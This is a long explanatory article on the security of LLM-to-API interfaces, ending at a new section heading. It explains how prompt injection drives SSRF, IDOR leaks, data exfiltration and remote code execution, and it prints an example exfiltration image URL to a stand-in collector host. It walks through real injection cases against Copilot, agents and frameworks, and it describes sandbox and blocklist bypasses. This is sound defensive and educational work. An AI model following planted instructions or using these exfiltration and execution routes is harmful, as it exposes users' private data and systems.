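# Security-first design of LLM-to-API interfaces: how data leaks escalate to remote code execution, and what reduces the risk

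## What is an LLM-to-API interface, and where can it be attacked?

A large language model (LLM) is a program that takes in text and produces more text. An application programming interface (API) is the set of requests that a piece of software accepts from other software. Weather services, databases, mail servers and payment systems all have APIs. A model cannot send these requests on its own, so developers write software around it, called the LLM-to-API interface. This software describes the available requests to the model, picks out any request in the model's output, carries it out and feeds the result back. It lets a chatbot look up an order, for example.

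The interface sends requests with the application's own access rights, but their content depends on the text the model has processed, some of which strangers may have written. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) examines eight classes of web attack that can run through a model, five with documented cases and three that the paper constructs by analogy. In its analysis, the model usually opens a new route to existing low-level flaws, such as a database that executes whatever query arrives, rather than adding new ones.

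### One question about a ticket price

The same two researchers built TicketOracle, a test application simple enough to follow from end to end. It is a concert website with a chat assistant and a database of events, ticket prices and user reviews. Suppose a user asks the assistant how much a Metallica ticket costs.

The application starts by filling in a prompt template. It joins the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), the conversation so far and the new question into one text, and adds a description of each tool. A tool is a function that the application offers to the model. TicketOracle has just one, `fetch_event_data`, which takes a web address, sends a request to it and returns the response, cut to a fixed length. The format below comes from the Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), part of the specification of an open standard for connecting models to outside software.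 In that format, a description of TicketOracle's tool could look like this:

```json
{
  "name": "fetch_event_data",
  "description": "Fetch the record of an event, including its ticket price",
  "inputSchema": {
    "type": "object",
    "properties": {
      "url": { "type": "string", "description": "Address of the event record" }
    },
    "required": ["url"]
  }
}
```

Given the question and this description, the model produces a tool call in place of an answer. A tool call is a structured request to run a tool with particular parameters (the address is a placeholder):

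```json
{
  "name": "fetch_event_data",
  "arguments": { "url": "https://tickets.example/events/metallica" }
}
```

The tool call is still only text, and the model has no network connection of its own, so nothing has happened outside the model yet. A parser turns the text into data that a program can use, and checks that the tool exists and that the arguments fit the schema. The schema above requires only that `url` be present and be a string, so the address of a machine on the company's internal network passes the check just as the address of a concert does.

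The step from parser to executor crosses a trust boundary, where data passes from a less trusted part of a system to a more trusted one and the receiving side has to check it. The model's output belongs on the less trusted side because anyone whose text went into the prompt may have influenced it. Developers can easily forget this, since the output is tidy JSON from a component they chose and configured.

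The executor then runs the function. The component that acts on the data is called the sink, and in TicketOracle it is the code that sends web requests. In other applications it may be a database engine, a command shell, a template renderer that fills in web pages, or a function such as Python's `eval()`, which runs a string as program code. What an attacker can gain depends mostly on the sink. With a web client, the classic result is server-side request forgery (SSRF), in which an attacker makes a server send requests to places that the server can reach and the attacker cannot. In TicketOracle, one such place is an administrative API with user records, which accepts connections only from programs on the same machine. The assistant's code runs on that machine, so a tool call containing the API's address would reach it. Security engineers call a program in this position a confused deputy,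 because someone who lacks its privileges can trick it into using them.

If the sink is a shell, a template renderer or `eval()`, the result can be remote code execution (RCE), in which attackers run code of their choice on a machine they do not control. An escalation path is the series of steps from limited access, such as reading data, to greater access, such as RCE.

When someone finds a flaw like this in published software, it normally receives a CVE (Common Vulnerabilities and Exposures) number, a public identifier made up of a year and a serial number. Most CVEs also have a severity score from 0 to 10 under the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), with 9.0 and above counted as critical. The score depends on factors such as whether the attack works over a network, whether the attacker needs an account and how much damage the attack can do. The US National Security Agency (NSA)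 guidance paper *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026) includes the example of CVE-2025-49596, a flaw in MCP Inspector, which is a program for testing tool servers during development. The program accepted unverified input, and crafted messages could make it run an attacker's code until version 0.14.1 fixed the flaw. Those messages went directly to the program, without passing through a model. A flaw that an attacker can exploit only through the action of a model is called an LLM-in-the-loop vulnerability.

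On the concert site, the API returns the event's record. The application appends this response to the conversation and calls the model again. *Web LLM attacks*, a training page from the web security company PortSwigger, describes this loop step by step. The API's response is now part of the model's context, the text from which it computes its next output. The model may produce another tool call, which repeats the loop, or it may write the reply that the user sees, with the price, venue and date.

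The return path also crosses a trust boundary, and developers overlook it more easily than the outgoing one. TicketOracle, like any site with user reviews, lets outsiders store text with an event, and the assistant receives that text when it fetches the event. Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. It is direct if the attacker types it into the chat, and indirect if it is in content that the model processes for someone else. In an example from PortSwigger, a user asks for a summary of their latest email. The email contains a request to forward all mail to another person, and the model responds with a tool call that creates the forwarding rule, which the user may never learn about.

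Attackers can also use tool descriptions, because these go into the context too. The NSA describes a demonstration in which researchers connected an assistant to both a trusted WhatsApp tool and a malicious server. The server showed a benign tool description at installation, then later replaced it with one that alone was enough to make the assistant disclose WhatsApp messages.

The reply is the last stage. A reply that contains data the user has no right to see is information disclosure, even if every component worked as designed. The reply can also reach a sink, such as a browser that renders the model's text as a web page and runs any script in it. Outgoing tool calls can disclose data too, because their parameters may carry private text to an outside service. The Model Context Protocol therefore recommends that applications show users a call's inputs before sending it.

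### Why the model cannot keep instructions and data apart

Web developers have met a similar problem before, in databases. SQL is the language in which programs query most databases, and a program can build a query in two ways:

```python
# The user's text becomes part of the command
query = "select price from events where artist = '" + artist + "'"
cursor.execute(query)

# The user's text stays a value
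query = "select price from events where artist = ?"
cursor.execute(query, [artist])
```

In the first version, a quotation mark in the user's text ends the artist's name early, and the database treats whatever follows as SQL, which is called SQL injection. The second version is a prepared statement, or parameterised query. The database takes the command's structure from the text with the placeholder and handles the artist's name separately, as a value. Whatever that value contains, the database only compares it with the names in the `artist` column. This protection does not rely on recognising malicious input, so it also works against input nobody has anticipated.

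A language model has no second channel of this kind. The system prompt, the user's question and the concert review all become tokens (words or fragments of words) in one sequence, and the model predicts the next token by running the same computation over the whole sequence. David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, makes this point central to *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (December 2025), writing that current models "simply do not enforce a security boundary" between instructions and data inside a prompt.

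Developers can mark the review as data, with tags or quotation marks, and model makers can train models to give such text less authority. David C accepts that these measures make attacks harder. But the marks are also tokens, and how the model treats them depends on learned probabilities. The software developer Willison (2022) records in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* that, within days of the first public demonstrations, an input got round one proposed fix, which was to wrap the user's text in JSON quotation marks. One OpenAI model of the time accepted the instruction and the input in separate fields, but instructions in the input field still took effect. Willison had hoped for an equivalent of the prepared statement, but by April 2023 he considered it extremely difficult, if not impossible, on the current architecture of these models.

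That is a judgement about how today's models work, and nobody has proved that a model with a real boundary is impossible, but the practical consequence for someone designing an interface now is the same. A programmer can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but David C calls the LLM "inherently confusable" and advises designers to assume the worst case, that the attacker has direct access to every tool the model can call.

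Prepared statements still work between the tool and the database when the developer writes the query and the model supplies only a value, such as an artist's name. The database then keeps that value separate from the command. Prepared statements don't give this protection when the model writes the whole query, as it does in some "ask your database" products, because the developer hasn't fixed the command in advance.

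### How models came to call APIs

Preamble, a security company, says in *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* (2022) that it reported the weakness privately to OpenAI on 3 May 2022. The weakness became widely known in September, when Riley Goodside posted examples in which GPT-3 was told to translate a sentence but followed the instructions in it instead. Willison named the attack "prompt injection" the next day, after SQL injection. The risk was small at first, because most applications only displayed the model's text. Greshake, Endres and colleagues introduced the indirect form in *Not what you've signed up for* (2023). They found that text on a web page, invisible to the user, could steer the Bing chatbot in the browser's sidebar, and they warned that injected text could control whether and how a model calls other APIs.

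On 23 March 2023, OpenAI launched plugins that let ChatGPT use third-party services (*ChatGPT plugins*, 2023), and on 13 June it added function calling for developers. As Willison (2023) explained that day, a developer sends the model a schema of the available functions, the model returns JSON naming the one to call, and the developer's own code runs it. Each company still had its own format until Anthropic released the Model Context Protocol (MCP) in November 2024. MCP has since become the common standard. Its development kits had more than 400 million downloads a month by July 2026, according to Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026). Since 2025, some agents (models that work through a task in many steps) also write short programs that call several APIs at once. The executor in such a system is a code interpreter, so running text from the model as code is normal and no longer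 a sign that something has gone wrong.

### What MCP requires, and what it leaves open

In MCP, an application such as a chat program contains a client that connects to servers offering tools. The client requests a list of tools from each server, passes their descriptions to the model, and forwards the model's tool calls to the right server. A server may run on a remote machine and communicate over HTTP, or run as a local process on the user's computer.

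Authorisation, the check on what a caller may do, is optional in the current version of the Model Context Protocol specification (*Authorization*, 28 July 2026). Implementations that support it over HTTP should follow a scheme based on OAuth 2.1, in which the user grants a program a token with limited permissions. Local servers should take their credentials from the environment they run in, which often means a password or key stored on the user's machine.

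The rules are stricter for servers that do use OAuth tokens. They must check that each token was meant for them, and must not accept or pass on any others. This prevents one old form of the confused deputy problem, in which a server uses a token that the user granted for a different service. The July revision also requires clients to check which authorisation server sent a response before they act on it (Model Context Protocol, 2026). But it did not make authorisation compulsory, so a complaint the NSA raised in May still applies. The agency found that many implementations lack authentication, and that those with it often do not distinguish between a caller who may read data and one who may delete it.

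Even complete authorisation would not prevent prompt injection. Suppose the concert site gave its assistant a tool for buying tickets and protected it with a correctly issued token. If a planted review led the model to call that tool, the call would carry the user's own valid token, and the server could not distinguish it from a purchase the user wanted. The specification addresses this case mainly by recommending that a human always be able to deny a tool call. Whether the human gets that chance depends on the application, because MCP "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level", according to a draft by the Model Context Protocol project.

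## How can a prompt make the interface disclose data?

A leak through an LLM-to-API interface usually begins with a request that the application is entitled to make. The database returns customer records because the query came from the application's account, and an internal server responds because the request came from a permitted machine. No component checks whether the person behind the request is allowed to see the result. That check can be missing when the model writes a database query, passes on a record number, or chooses an address to fetch. The model's output can also carry data to an outside server, for example in the URL of a link or image.

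### A query that is too broad

Pedro, Carreira and colleagues (2023), in *From Prompt Injections to SQL Injection Attacks*, studied chatbots that answer questions from a database. They built a small job-listing website with a table of users and one of job postings, and connected a chatbot to it through LangChain, a library for building applications around language models.

Suppose a user asks for the five best-paid jobs in London. LangChain puts the question into a prompt template, along with the names of the database's tables and columns. The template asks the model for an SQL query and then an answer. LangChain stops the model as soon as the query is complete, because the model would otherwise invent the results. LangChain then runs the query, adds the returned rows to the prompt, and calls the model again to write a reply in plain English.

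This process never compares the query with what the user is allowed to see, and the chatbot's database account could read and change every table. When the researchers asked for the contents of the users table, the model (GPT-3.5) wrote a valid query for everyone's names, email addresses and phone numbers, and the database ran it. The attack required neither trickery nor knowledge of SQL, and it worked all 30 times they repeated it.

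The researchers then added a rule to the prompt. The application filled in the ID of the user who was asking, and the prompt told the model to return only that user's rows. This stopped some attacks. When user 1 asked for user 2's email address, the model wrote a query with both conditions:

```sql
select email from users where user_id = 2 and user_id = 1
```

No row can satisfy both conditions, so the result was empty. But an attacker who simply claimed to be user 2 got the address, again in all 30 runs. The same attack worked on the six other models in the study, including GPT-4, at least in the simpler of LangChain's two chatbot designs, which runs one query per question.

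Those models are now several generations old. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tried similar techniques on newer models in 2026 without success, but they didn't try to improve the prompts. Even a model that resists manipulation can leak data without being manipulated. Black Lantern Security's *Artificial Foolishness* describes a test of a client's public chatbot in which every attempt to get the model past its limits failed. Then the chatbot itself offered to pull the first 100 entries of a table. The tester accepted and received 100 rows of sensitive customer data. The client took the chatbot offline the same day.

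### A record number that nobody checks

The developer can avoid model-written queries by fixing the query in advance and letting the model supply one value. Sumit Shah described an order chatbot with this design in November 2025, and Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian analyse it. The model took an order number from the conversation and passed it to a lookup function, which returned the matching order to anyone who asked.

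A stranger could therefore type in someone else's order number and ask for the email address on the order, then the delivery address, and then the details of several orders at once. Every order number combined the same three letters with six digits, so there were at most a million to try, and the chatbot did not limit how many requests a visitor could make.

Security engineers call this flaw an insecure direct object reference (IDOR), and it is common in ordinary web applications too. A prepared statement does not prevent it, because another customer's order number is a perfectly valid value. What the query lacks is a condition on who owns the order:

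```python
# Returns the order to anyone who knows or guesses its number
cursor.execute("select * from orders where order_id = ?", [order_id])

# Returns the order only to the customer who placed it
cursor.execute(
    "select * from orders where order_id = ? and customer_id = ?",
    [order_id, session.customer_id],
)
```

In the second version, the customer number comes from the login session, which the model cannot change. The rule is almost the same as the one Pedro and colleagues put in their prompt, but here the program applies it, so claiming to be someone else has no effect.

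Chatbots on shopping sites often serve visitors who have not logged in, so the customer number can't be taken from a login session. Tenable, a security company, found that Yuma AI Chat, a chatbot service used by multiple online shops, gave such visitors a customer's purchases and shipping address. The visitor needed only an order number or the customer's email address, which is hardly secret. Tenable's advisory, numbered 2026, lists no known solution.

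### An address inside the network

TicketOracle, the concert site from the previous section, has a tool that fetches any web address. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian published an experiment with it in August 2026. Their attacker is an outsider with no account who can chat with the assistant and store text with an event, but cannot reach the administrative API directly.

To read the user records, the attacker gives the assistant the API's internal address and a pretext for fetching it. The assistant's tool fetches the records, and the model summarises them in its reply. The address is often easy to guess because administrative pages tend to have conventional names.

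The researchers tried four direct attacks of this kind. They had the assistant read user records, probe a network port (its reply shows whether a service is listening there), and delete a record. The fourth attack was a "blind" request, which changes data on the server but returns an empty response, so they checked a server log to see whether it had arrived. In a fifth, indirect attack, they planted instructions in a concert review, and the assistant read them when an ordinary user asked about the event.

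The table gives the number of successful trials out of ten for each scenario on each of seven models, tested in April 2026. For attacks that return data, a trial counted as successful only if the assistant both sent the request and repeated the result to the user.

| Model | Port probing | Reading user records | Deleting a record | Blind request | Planted review, basic prompt | Planted review, hardened prompt |
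|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The application was the same for every model, so the differences in the first five columns come from the models. Llama 3.3 carried out every direct attack, while GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 carried out none. GPT-oss never disclosed the user records when the attacker asked for them directly, yet it deleted a record every time the attacker asked it to. Qwen and DeepSeek followed almost every instruction the attacker typed but never acted on the planted review. A developer could not have predicted this pattern from how harmful each request was.

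The deletions also depended on a design mistake in TicketOracle's administrative API, which deletes records in response to GET requests. By convention, GET requests only read data, and they are the only kind the tool can send.

These counts are less precise than they look. All ten trials of a scenario took place in one conversation, so the model had its earlier answers in context from the second trial on. Claude Opus 4.6 began the port-probing scenario with long explanations and ended it with refusals of barely more than a word. A score of 10 or 0 may therefore partly reflect a single early success or refusal. Even if the trials had been independent, ten refusals would leave a true success rate of one in ten quite possible.

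The last column shows the results with a hardened system prompt, which listed the permitted URL patterns and events and instructed the model to refuse everything else. With this prompt, all four direct attacks failed on every model. But the list was only an instruction, and the tool would still fetch any address the model gave it. To exploit this, the planted review included a fake system notice that the internal address was now on the list. This attack's successes fell from 5 to 0 out of 10 for GPT-oss and rose from 6 to 10 for Llama 3.3.

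Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian conclude that the hardening amplified the attack on Llama. It may have, but they also added text to the review for the hardened version to get around the list, so the experiment cannot separate the effects of the two changes. In all ten trials, Llama fetched an address that was not on its list. A check in the tool's own code would have blocked these requests.

### How the data gets out

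In the planted-review attack, the private records appeared in the reply to an ordinary user who had asked what people thought of the concert. That user had no right to see them, so this was information disclosure, but the attacker who wrote the review never received them. To receive data, an attacker who plants text also needs a way to send it from the victim's session to a server they control.

Injected instructions can make the model add private text to the address of a clickable link. When the user clicks it, the browser sends the whole address to the attacker's server. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes such an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, in which a phishing email made Copilot search the victim's inbox and put what it found into a link in invisible characters. Microsoft fixed the flaw in July 2024. Amazon fixed a similar flaw in its assistant Amazon Q for Business by no longer displaying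 links.

Images make the click unnecessary. If a chat window displays images, the browser requests each one as soon as it appears. Suppose the model's reply contains an image with this address:

```text
https://collector.example/revenue-down-12-percent.png
```

The request for the image sends the sentence about revenue to whoever runs `collector.example`, whether or not the image exists. The victim sees at most a broken picture.

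Data can also leak through a network lookup. Before a computer contacts a server by name, it looks up the server's numerical address in the Domain Name System (DNS). Lookups for names under an attacker's domain go to a name server that the attacker runs, so private text placed in the name arrives there even if the computer never makes a connection. SalesBleed, an attack on Salesforce's Agentforce agents, used DNS in this way. According to *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* (Poireault, 2026), researchers at Zenity Labs hid instructions in a public web form whose entries go straight into a company's customer records. When an agent later processed the record, it retrieved account data such as company names and deal sizes and sent them out through DNS. This bypassed a Salesforce safeguard that removed links to untrusted addresses. Salesforce finished fixing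 the problem on 18 August 2026.

The request that carries the data out can come from outside the victim's computer. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research agent when it had access to a user's Gmail account. Hidden text in an email told the agent to find sensitive data in the inbox and visit a web address containing that data. The request left from OpenAI's servers, where the agent ran, so a company watching its own network and its employees' browsers could have seen nothing unusual. OpenAI fixed the flaw in August 2025.

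### The lethal trifecta

These attacks through planted text rely on three capabilities that Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, warns against combining in one system: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. If a system has all three, an attacker can plant an instruction that makes the model collect the data and send it out. Willison advises people who combine tools themselves to avoid having all three together, because nobody knows how to reliably stop a model from following planted instructions.

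This advice is useful because a developer can check the three conditions by listing the system's tools and data sources, without having to predict how an attacker will phrase an instruction. But it is hard to recognise every source of untrusted content and every route by which data can leave, as a series of attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot shows.

**EchoLeak (2025).** Researchers at Aim Security found this flaw in January 2025, and it later received the number CVE-2025-32711. An attacker only had to send an email to an employee of the target company. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, reconstruct the steps:

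1. The email contained instructions for Copilot, phrased as an ordinary business request to the human recipient. Microsoft's filter for prompt injection did not flag it.
2. The employee later asked Copilot about something at work. Copilot searched the employee's mail and files for relevant material, and the attacker's email came into the context along with internal documents.
3. Following the instructions, Copilot put sensitive details from the context into the address of an image in its reply. Another filter removed external links, but it did not recognise the notation that the attack used.
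4. The employee's browser tried to load the image. Copilot's page had a content security policy, a list of the domains from which the browser may load things, and the attacker's domain was not on it. But a Microsoft Teams service was, and this service would fetch any address passed to it. The image request went to Teams, and Teams forwarded the data to the attacker's server.

The attack met all three of Willison's conditions and needed each one to succeed. If Copilot had been unable to read internal files, the attacker would have had nothing worth stealing. If it had kept outside email separate from internal documents, the instructions would not have reached the model while it was handling private data. If the chat window had not loaded images from addresses the model wrote, the data would have stayed in the employee's browser, at least until someone clicked a link.

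Microsoft had defended two of these points by filtering incoming text and restricting outgoing requests, but both defences failed because each covered less than it appeared to. The domain list, for example, controlled which servers the browser contacted but not what those servers did next. This last step is server-side request forgery again, with Teams as the confused deputy.

Microsoft fixed EchoLeak on its own servers in May 2025, before the public learned of it, and reported no known attacks on customers. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* reports that Microsoft rated its severity 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5.

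**SearchLeak (2026).** A year later, the security company Varonis found another way to get data out of the same product, documented in *SearchLeak*. The attack requires the victim to click once on a link to a genuine Microsoft address. The link opens Copilot's enterprise search page with a search already filled in. Copilot treated this search text as a prompt and followed its instructions to find an email and put the email's title into an image address.

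To guard against images in replies, Microsoft's page wrapped the model's output in code formatting so that the browser would show it as plain text. But the page did this only after the reply was complete. The browser displayed the reply as it came in, so it had already requested the image. The content security policy blocked unknown domains, as it had in EchoLeak, but it allowed Microsoft's search engine, Bing. Bing's image search fetches any picture whose address it receives, and it passed the email title on to the attacker's server.

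SearchLeak also meets the three conditions. The attacker's text arrived in the link, not in an email or document that Copilot retrieved, and it looked to the application like something the user had typed. Willison's definition of untrusted content includes any mechanism by which an attacker's text can reach the model, so it covers the link. A developer who listed only the documents and messages that Copilot reads would have overlooked it.

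The flaw could expose anything the victim could open, including emails with security codes and password-reset links, which an attacker could use to get into other accounts. Microsoft rated the flaw (CVE-2026-42824) critical and fixed it.

**ReLeak (2026).** On 3 December 2026, Cato AI Labs disclosed three more attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, which again began with an email the victim did not have to open. The data left through an image address, a link to a saved file, or code that Copilot ran. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) reports that Microsoft fixed them between 17 September and 15 November, and that Cato knew of no real attacks. It also reports that Microsoft's documentation described a block on outgoing traffic from the sandbox, the isolated environment for running code, but the block failed. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak*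 (2026) explains that the image route went through Bing, although Microsoft had fixed SearchLeak months earlier.

Willison observed in 2025 that vendors almost always respond to such reports by closing the specific route by which data could leave. Copilot's record suggests that this is a weak strategy for a product with so many routes. Microsoft closed the link route in 2024 and the Teams route in 2025, and researchers found new ones in 2026. The other two conditions are harder to remove, because an assistant that could not read a company's files or incoming mail would be of little use in an office.

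### Leaks that need only two conditions

The trifecta describes theft from someone else's session. When the attacker is the user, the attack works without any text from a third party. It needs only private data and a way to get it out, which the chat window provides. This was the case with the dump of the users table, the two order chatbots, Black Lantern Security's hundred rows and the direct attack on TicketOracle's user records.

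These leaks meet all three conditions if the attacker's own message counts as untrusted content. Every public chatbot then has untrusted content and a way for data to leave from the start, so private data is the only condition the developer can still change. Whether or not the message counts, blocking images and outside links does nothing against these leaks. Preventing them requires tools that return only data the person asking has a right to see.

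The attack using TicketOracle's planted review relied on a different pair, private data and untrusted content. It did not require an outside connection because the records went to another customer.

If a tool can write data, an attacker may not need a hidden channel to get private data out. In one test, Pedro and colleagues planted instructions in a job posting. When another user of the site asked the chatbot about the postings, it replaced that user's email address in the database with the attacker's, then answered the question without mentioning the planted posting. This worked in all 30 runs with GPT-3.5. No private data had left the database yet, but on a site that sends password resets by email, the attacker could now request one and log in as the victim.

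## How does text written by a model become running code?

A model's output becomes running code when software passes it to a component that executes it. Developers sometimes do this on purpose so the model can draw charts or run commands. In other cases they do it by accident, because they believe the output is plain data.

Ma, Rong and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities*, traced how the model's output reached the dangerous operation in 41 LLM-in-the-loop vulnerabilities. They found five routes:

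| Route | What the model supplies | What acts on it | Example |
|---|---|---|---|
| Generated code or expressions | A program or formula | An interpreter, through functions such as `exec()` or `eval()` | Vanna.AI, CVE-2024-5565 |
| Generated queries | A database query | The database engine | LlamaIndex, CVE-2024-12911 |
| Tool actions | The choice of a tool, or its arguments | The tool, with its own privileges | AWS MCP server, CVE-2025-5277 |
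| Rendered output | HTML, Markdown or other page content | Usually a browser | ChuanhuChatGPT, CVE-2024-3402 |
| Parsed or dispatched output | Text in a structured format | A parser or handler | vLLM, CVE-2025-9141 |

Not every case ends in remote code execution on a server. Rendered output usually runs in the viewer's browser, and a generated query may only create a file.

### Charts drawn by generated code

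Vanna.AI is a Python library for questioning a database in plain language. Researchers at the software company JFrog suspected that it would allow SQL injection, but they found a more serious problem in the feature that draws charts. JFrog's *When Prompts Go Rogue* (2024) traces the path from question to code:

1. The model turns the user's question into an SQL query, and the library runs it.
2. The library sends the model a second prompt with the question, the query and a description of the resulting columns. This prompt asks for Python code that plots the data.
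3. The library passes the code to `exec()`, which runs any Python program it receives.

The chart feature was on by default. To exploit it, an attacker had to get an instruction into the second prompt, but the question first had to produce valid SQL. When the researchers told the model to ignore its instructions and laugh, it did, and the database returned a syntax error because the output was not valid SQL.

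A valid SQL query can return a fixed piece of text, so they then used that text to give the model an instruction. The library copied the whole query into the second prompt, and the model put the researchers' line of Python at the top of the chart code. The line only listed the files in the current directory. The prompt had asked for only plotting code, but `exec()` runs any Python code it is given.

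The maintainer of Vanna.AI responded with a hardening guide, which helps only developers who read and follow it. JFrog recommended checking the model's output and running generated code in a sandbox.

### A city name that became a program

Text from a model can become running code even if the model doesn't write a program. In May 2026, Microsoft described two flaws its researchers had found in Semantic Kernel, the company's open-source framework for building agents. In one of them, CVE-2026-26030, the model supplied only a city name.

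The researchers demonstrated it with a hotel finder. When a user asks for hotels in Paris, the model calls a search tool with "Paris" as the city. The framework first filters the list to hotels in that city, then ranks them by how closely they match the request. To build the filter, Semantic Kernel wrote a small Python function as text, inserted the city name, and had `eval()` turn the text into a working function. In simplified form, this is the unsafe design next to a safe one:

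```python
# The model's text becomes part of a program
matches = eval("lambda x: x.city == '" + city + "'")

# The model's text stays a value
matches = lambda x: x.city == city
```

A `lambda` is a short function without a name. The first version has the weakness that SQL injection exploits, because a quotation mark in the city name lets the rest of the name run as code. The second version, like a prepared statement, only compares the name with each hotel's city.

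The framework's developers had seen the danger and added a validator that checked the text before it reached `eval()`. The validator converted the text into a syntax tree, which represents the code's structure, and rejected anything other than a single lambda. It also searched the tree for forbidden names, such as `eval`, `exec` and `open`. Code that passed both checks ran in an environment without Python's built-in functions.

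One prompt got past the blocklist, the lambda check and the removal of built-in functions, and started the calculator program on the machine running the agent. The blocklist lacked several names that the attack used, including the function that passes a command to the shell. The attack passed the lambda check because it fitted inside a lambda. Removing the built-in functions did not stop it because it never called them directly.

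The last failure comes from how Python works. Every value in Python is an object with a link to its class, and classes have links to other classes that the program has loaded. Starting from even an empty list, code can follow these links to the machinery that imports modules, and from there to the operating system. A blocklist has to cover every such path, including those its developers do not know about, because an attacker needs only one. This makes blocklists fragile in dynamic languages like Python, which let a running program inspect and use much of its own environment.

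An allowlist can fail too if it restricts the wrong thing. Reiner (2024), in *Anatomy of an LLM RCE*, examined the calculator tool in LoLLMs, a program that offers many models through one interface. The calculator also used `eval()` without built-in functions, and it let expressions look up only names from Python's mathematics module. Reiner bypassed this list by starting from a plain value and following the links between objects, which didn't require looking up a forbidden name. The LoLLMs developers fixed the flaw, CVE-2024-6982.

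Microsoft's fix for Semantic Kernel restricts the structure of the filter as well as its names. It has four parts:

- An allowlist of syntax permits comparisons, logical operators, arithmetic, plain values and a few other safe constructs. Most of the language is no longer available to a filter.
- A second allowlist covers function calls, so an expression that somehow reached a dangerous function still could not call it.
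- The only name that may stand on its own is the lambda's parameter, `x` in the example. This removes direct references to `eval` or to the operating system module.
- A blocklist forbids the attributes that lead from an object to its class and onwards.

The blocklist remains because the filter has to read `x.city` and so cannot forbid attributes altogether. But it now has three allowlists around it, so an attribute name missing from it would no longer be enough for an attack like the first.

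The flaw affected Python versions of the framework before 1.39.4, and only agents whose search tool used the in-memory data store with its default filter. For developers who could not update, GitLab's *CVE-2026-26030* (2026) lists avoiding that store in production as a workaround.

### Queries that do more than read

Prepared statements give no protection when the model writes the whole query, so the developer has to limit what the query may do instead.

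LlamaIndex, a framework for connecting models to data, passed SQL from the model directly to SQLite, a database engine that stores each database in a file. SQLite's `ATTACH DATABASE` command opens another database file and creates it if it does not exist. An attacker who influenced the query could therefore create files on the machine (CVE-2024-12911). Creating a file does not itself run code, but it can lead to code execution if another program later executes or loads that file.

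Ma and colleagues compared two repairs of this flaw. An AI coding agent wrote a filter that searched the query for dangerous keywords, but the filter also rejected harmless queries, such as one with a column named "attach". The LlamaIndex developers instead used SQLite's authoriser, a function that the engine calls to check each action a query would perform. It blocks attaching a database but still permits ordinary reads.

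The authoriser works better than a keyword filter because SQLite calls it after parsing has established whether "attach" is a command or just a name. A keyword filter checks only the text, so an attacker can look for a wording that it misclassifies.

### Tool calls with the wrong arguments

In a tool action, the harm comes from what the tool does with the arguments that the model supplies.

The AWS MCP server lets an assistant manage resources in Amazon's cloud. Its vendor is an independent developer, alexei-led, not Amazon (GCVE, 2025). Before running a command for Amazon's command-line program, the server's tool checked that the command began with `aws` and did not directly call certain critical services. But a shell accepts several commands on one line, so an attacker could add a second command after a valid first one (CVE-2025-5277).

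Such a server usually runs on a developer's own computer and accepts no connections from outside. Snyk's *Prompt Injection Meets MCP* (2025) shows how an attacker could still reach it through the model. The developer downloads a code repository that has an encoded instruction in a comment in one file. In Snyk's test, the developer then had to refer to that file by name in Cursor, an AI code editor, as is ordinary before changing a file. Downloading the repository and asking vague questions about it were not enough.

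The model then decoded the comment, which contained instructions to add an extra command to every later call of the AWS tool and not to mention it. When the developer asked for a list of storage folders, Cursor displayed the tool call and waited for approval. The call began with the command the developer expected and ended with the extra one, which a busy person could easily miss.

Snyk reported the flaw on 8 April 2025. The maintainer released a fix two days later, but it was incomplete, and the maintainer fully fixed the flaw only after Snyk pointed out the remaining vulnerable code. The injected command runs with the server's privileges. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian note that for a cloud tool these may include the developer's access to the company's cloud account.

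### A download function that the model was never meant to see

The second Semantic Kernel flaw, CVE-2026-25592, also follows this route, but the mistake was offering the tool at all. One of the framework's plugins lets an agent run Python code in a sandbox in Microsoft's cloud. Code in the sandbox cannot access the host, the machine that runs the agent. Two helper functions on the host move files into and out of the sandbox.

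In the .NET version of the framework, a developer had by accident marked the download function with the label `[KernelFunction]`. The framework offers every function with this label to the model as a tool. The model could therefore choose all the function's parameters, including the place on the host where it saved the file, and the function did not check that place. Microsoft describes an attack in three steps:

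1. An injected prompt makes the agent write a malicious script inside the sandbox, where it can do no harm to the host.
2. A second instruction makes the agent download the script to the host's Startup folder.
3. Windows runs the script the next time someone signs in, because it runs everything in that folder.

The sandbox itself had no software flaw. The attacker could get out through the download function, a legitimate feature that the model was allowed to call. In both the .NET and Python versions, the upload function accepted any path on the host, so an injected prompt could make the model copy private keys into the sandbox.

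Microsoft made two changes to the download function in .NET version 1.71.0. It removed the label, which hides the function from the model and stops the model from calling it. This is enough to break the attack. Microsoft also added a check that works out the file's true location and compares it with a list of permitted folders, which limits the damage if a developer's own code passes the function an unsafe path. For uploads, Microsoft added similar protection that developers have to switch on themselves.

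According to NVD's *CVE-2026-25592 Detail*, developers unable to update could, as a temporary measure, intercept each call to the two functions and allow only approved file paths.

### A coding agent that grants itself permission

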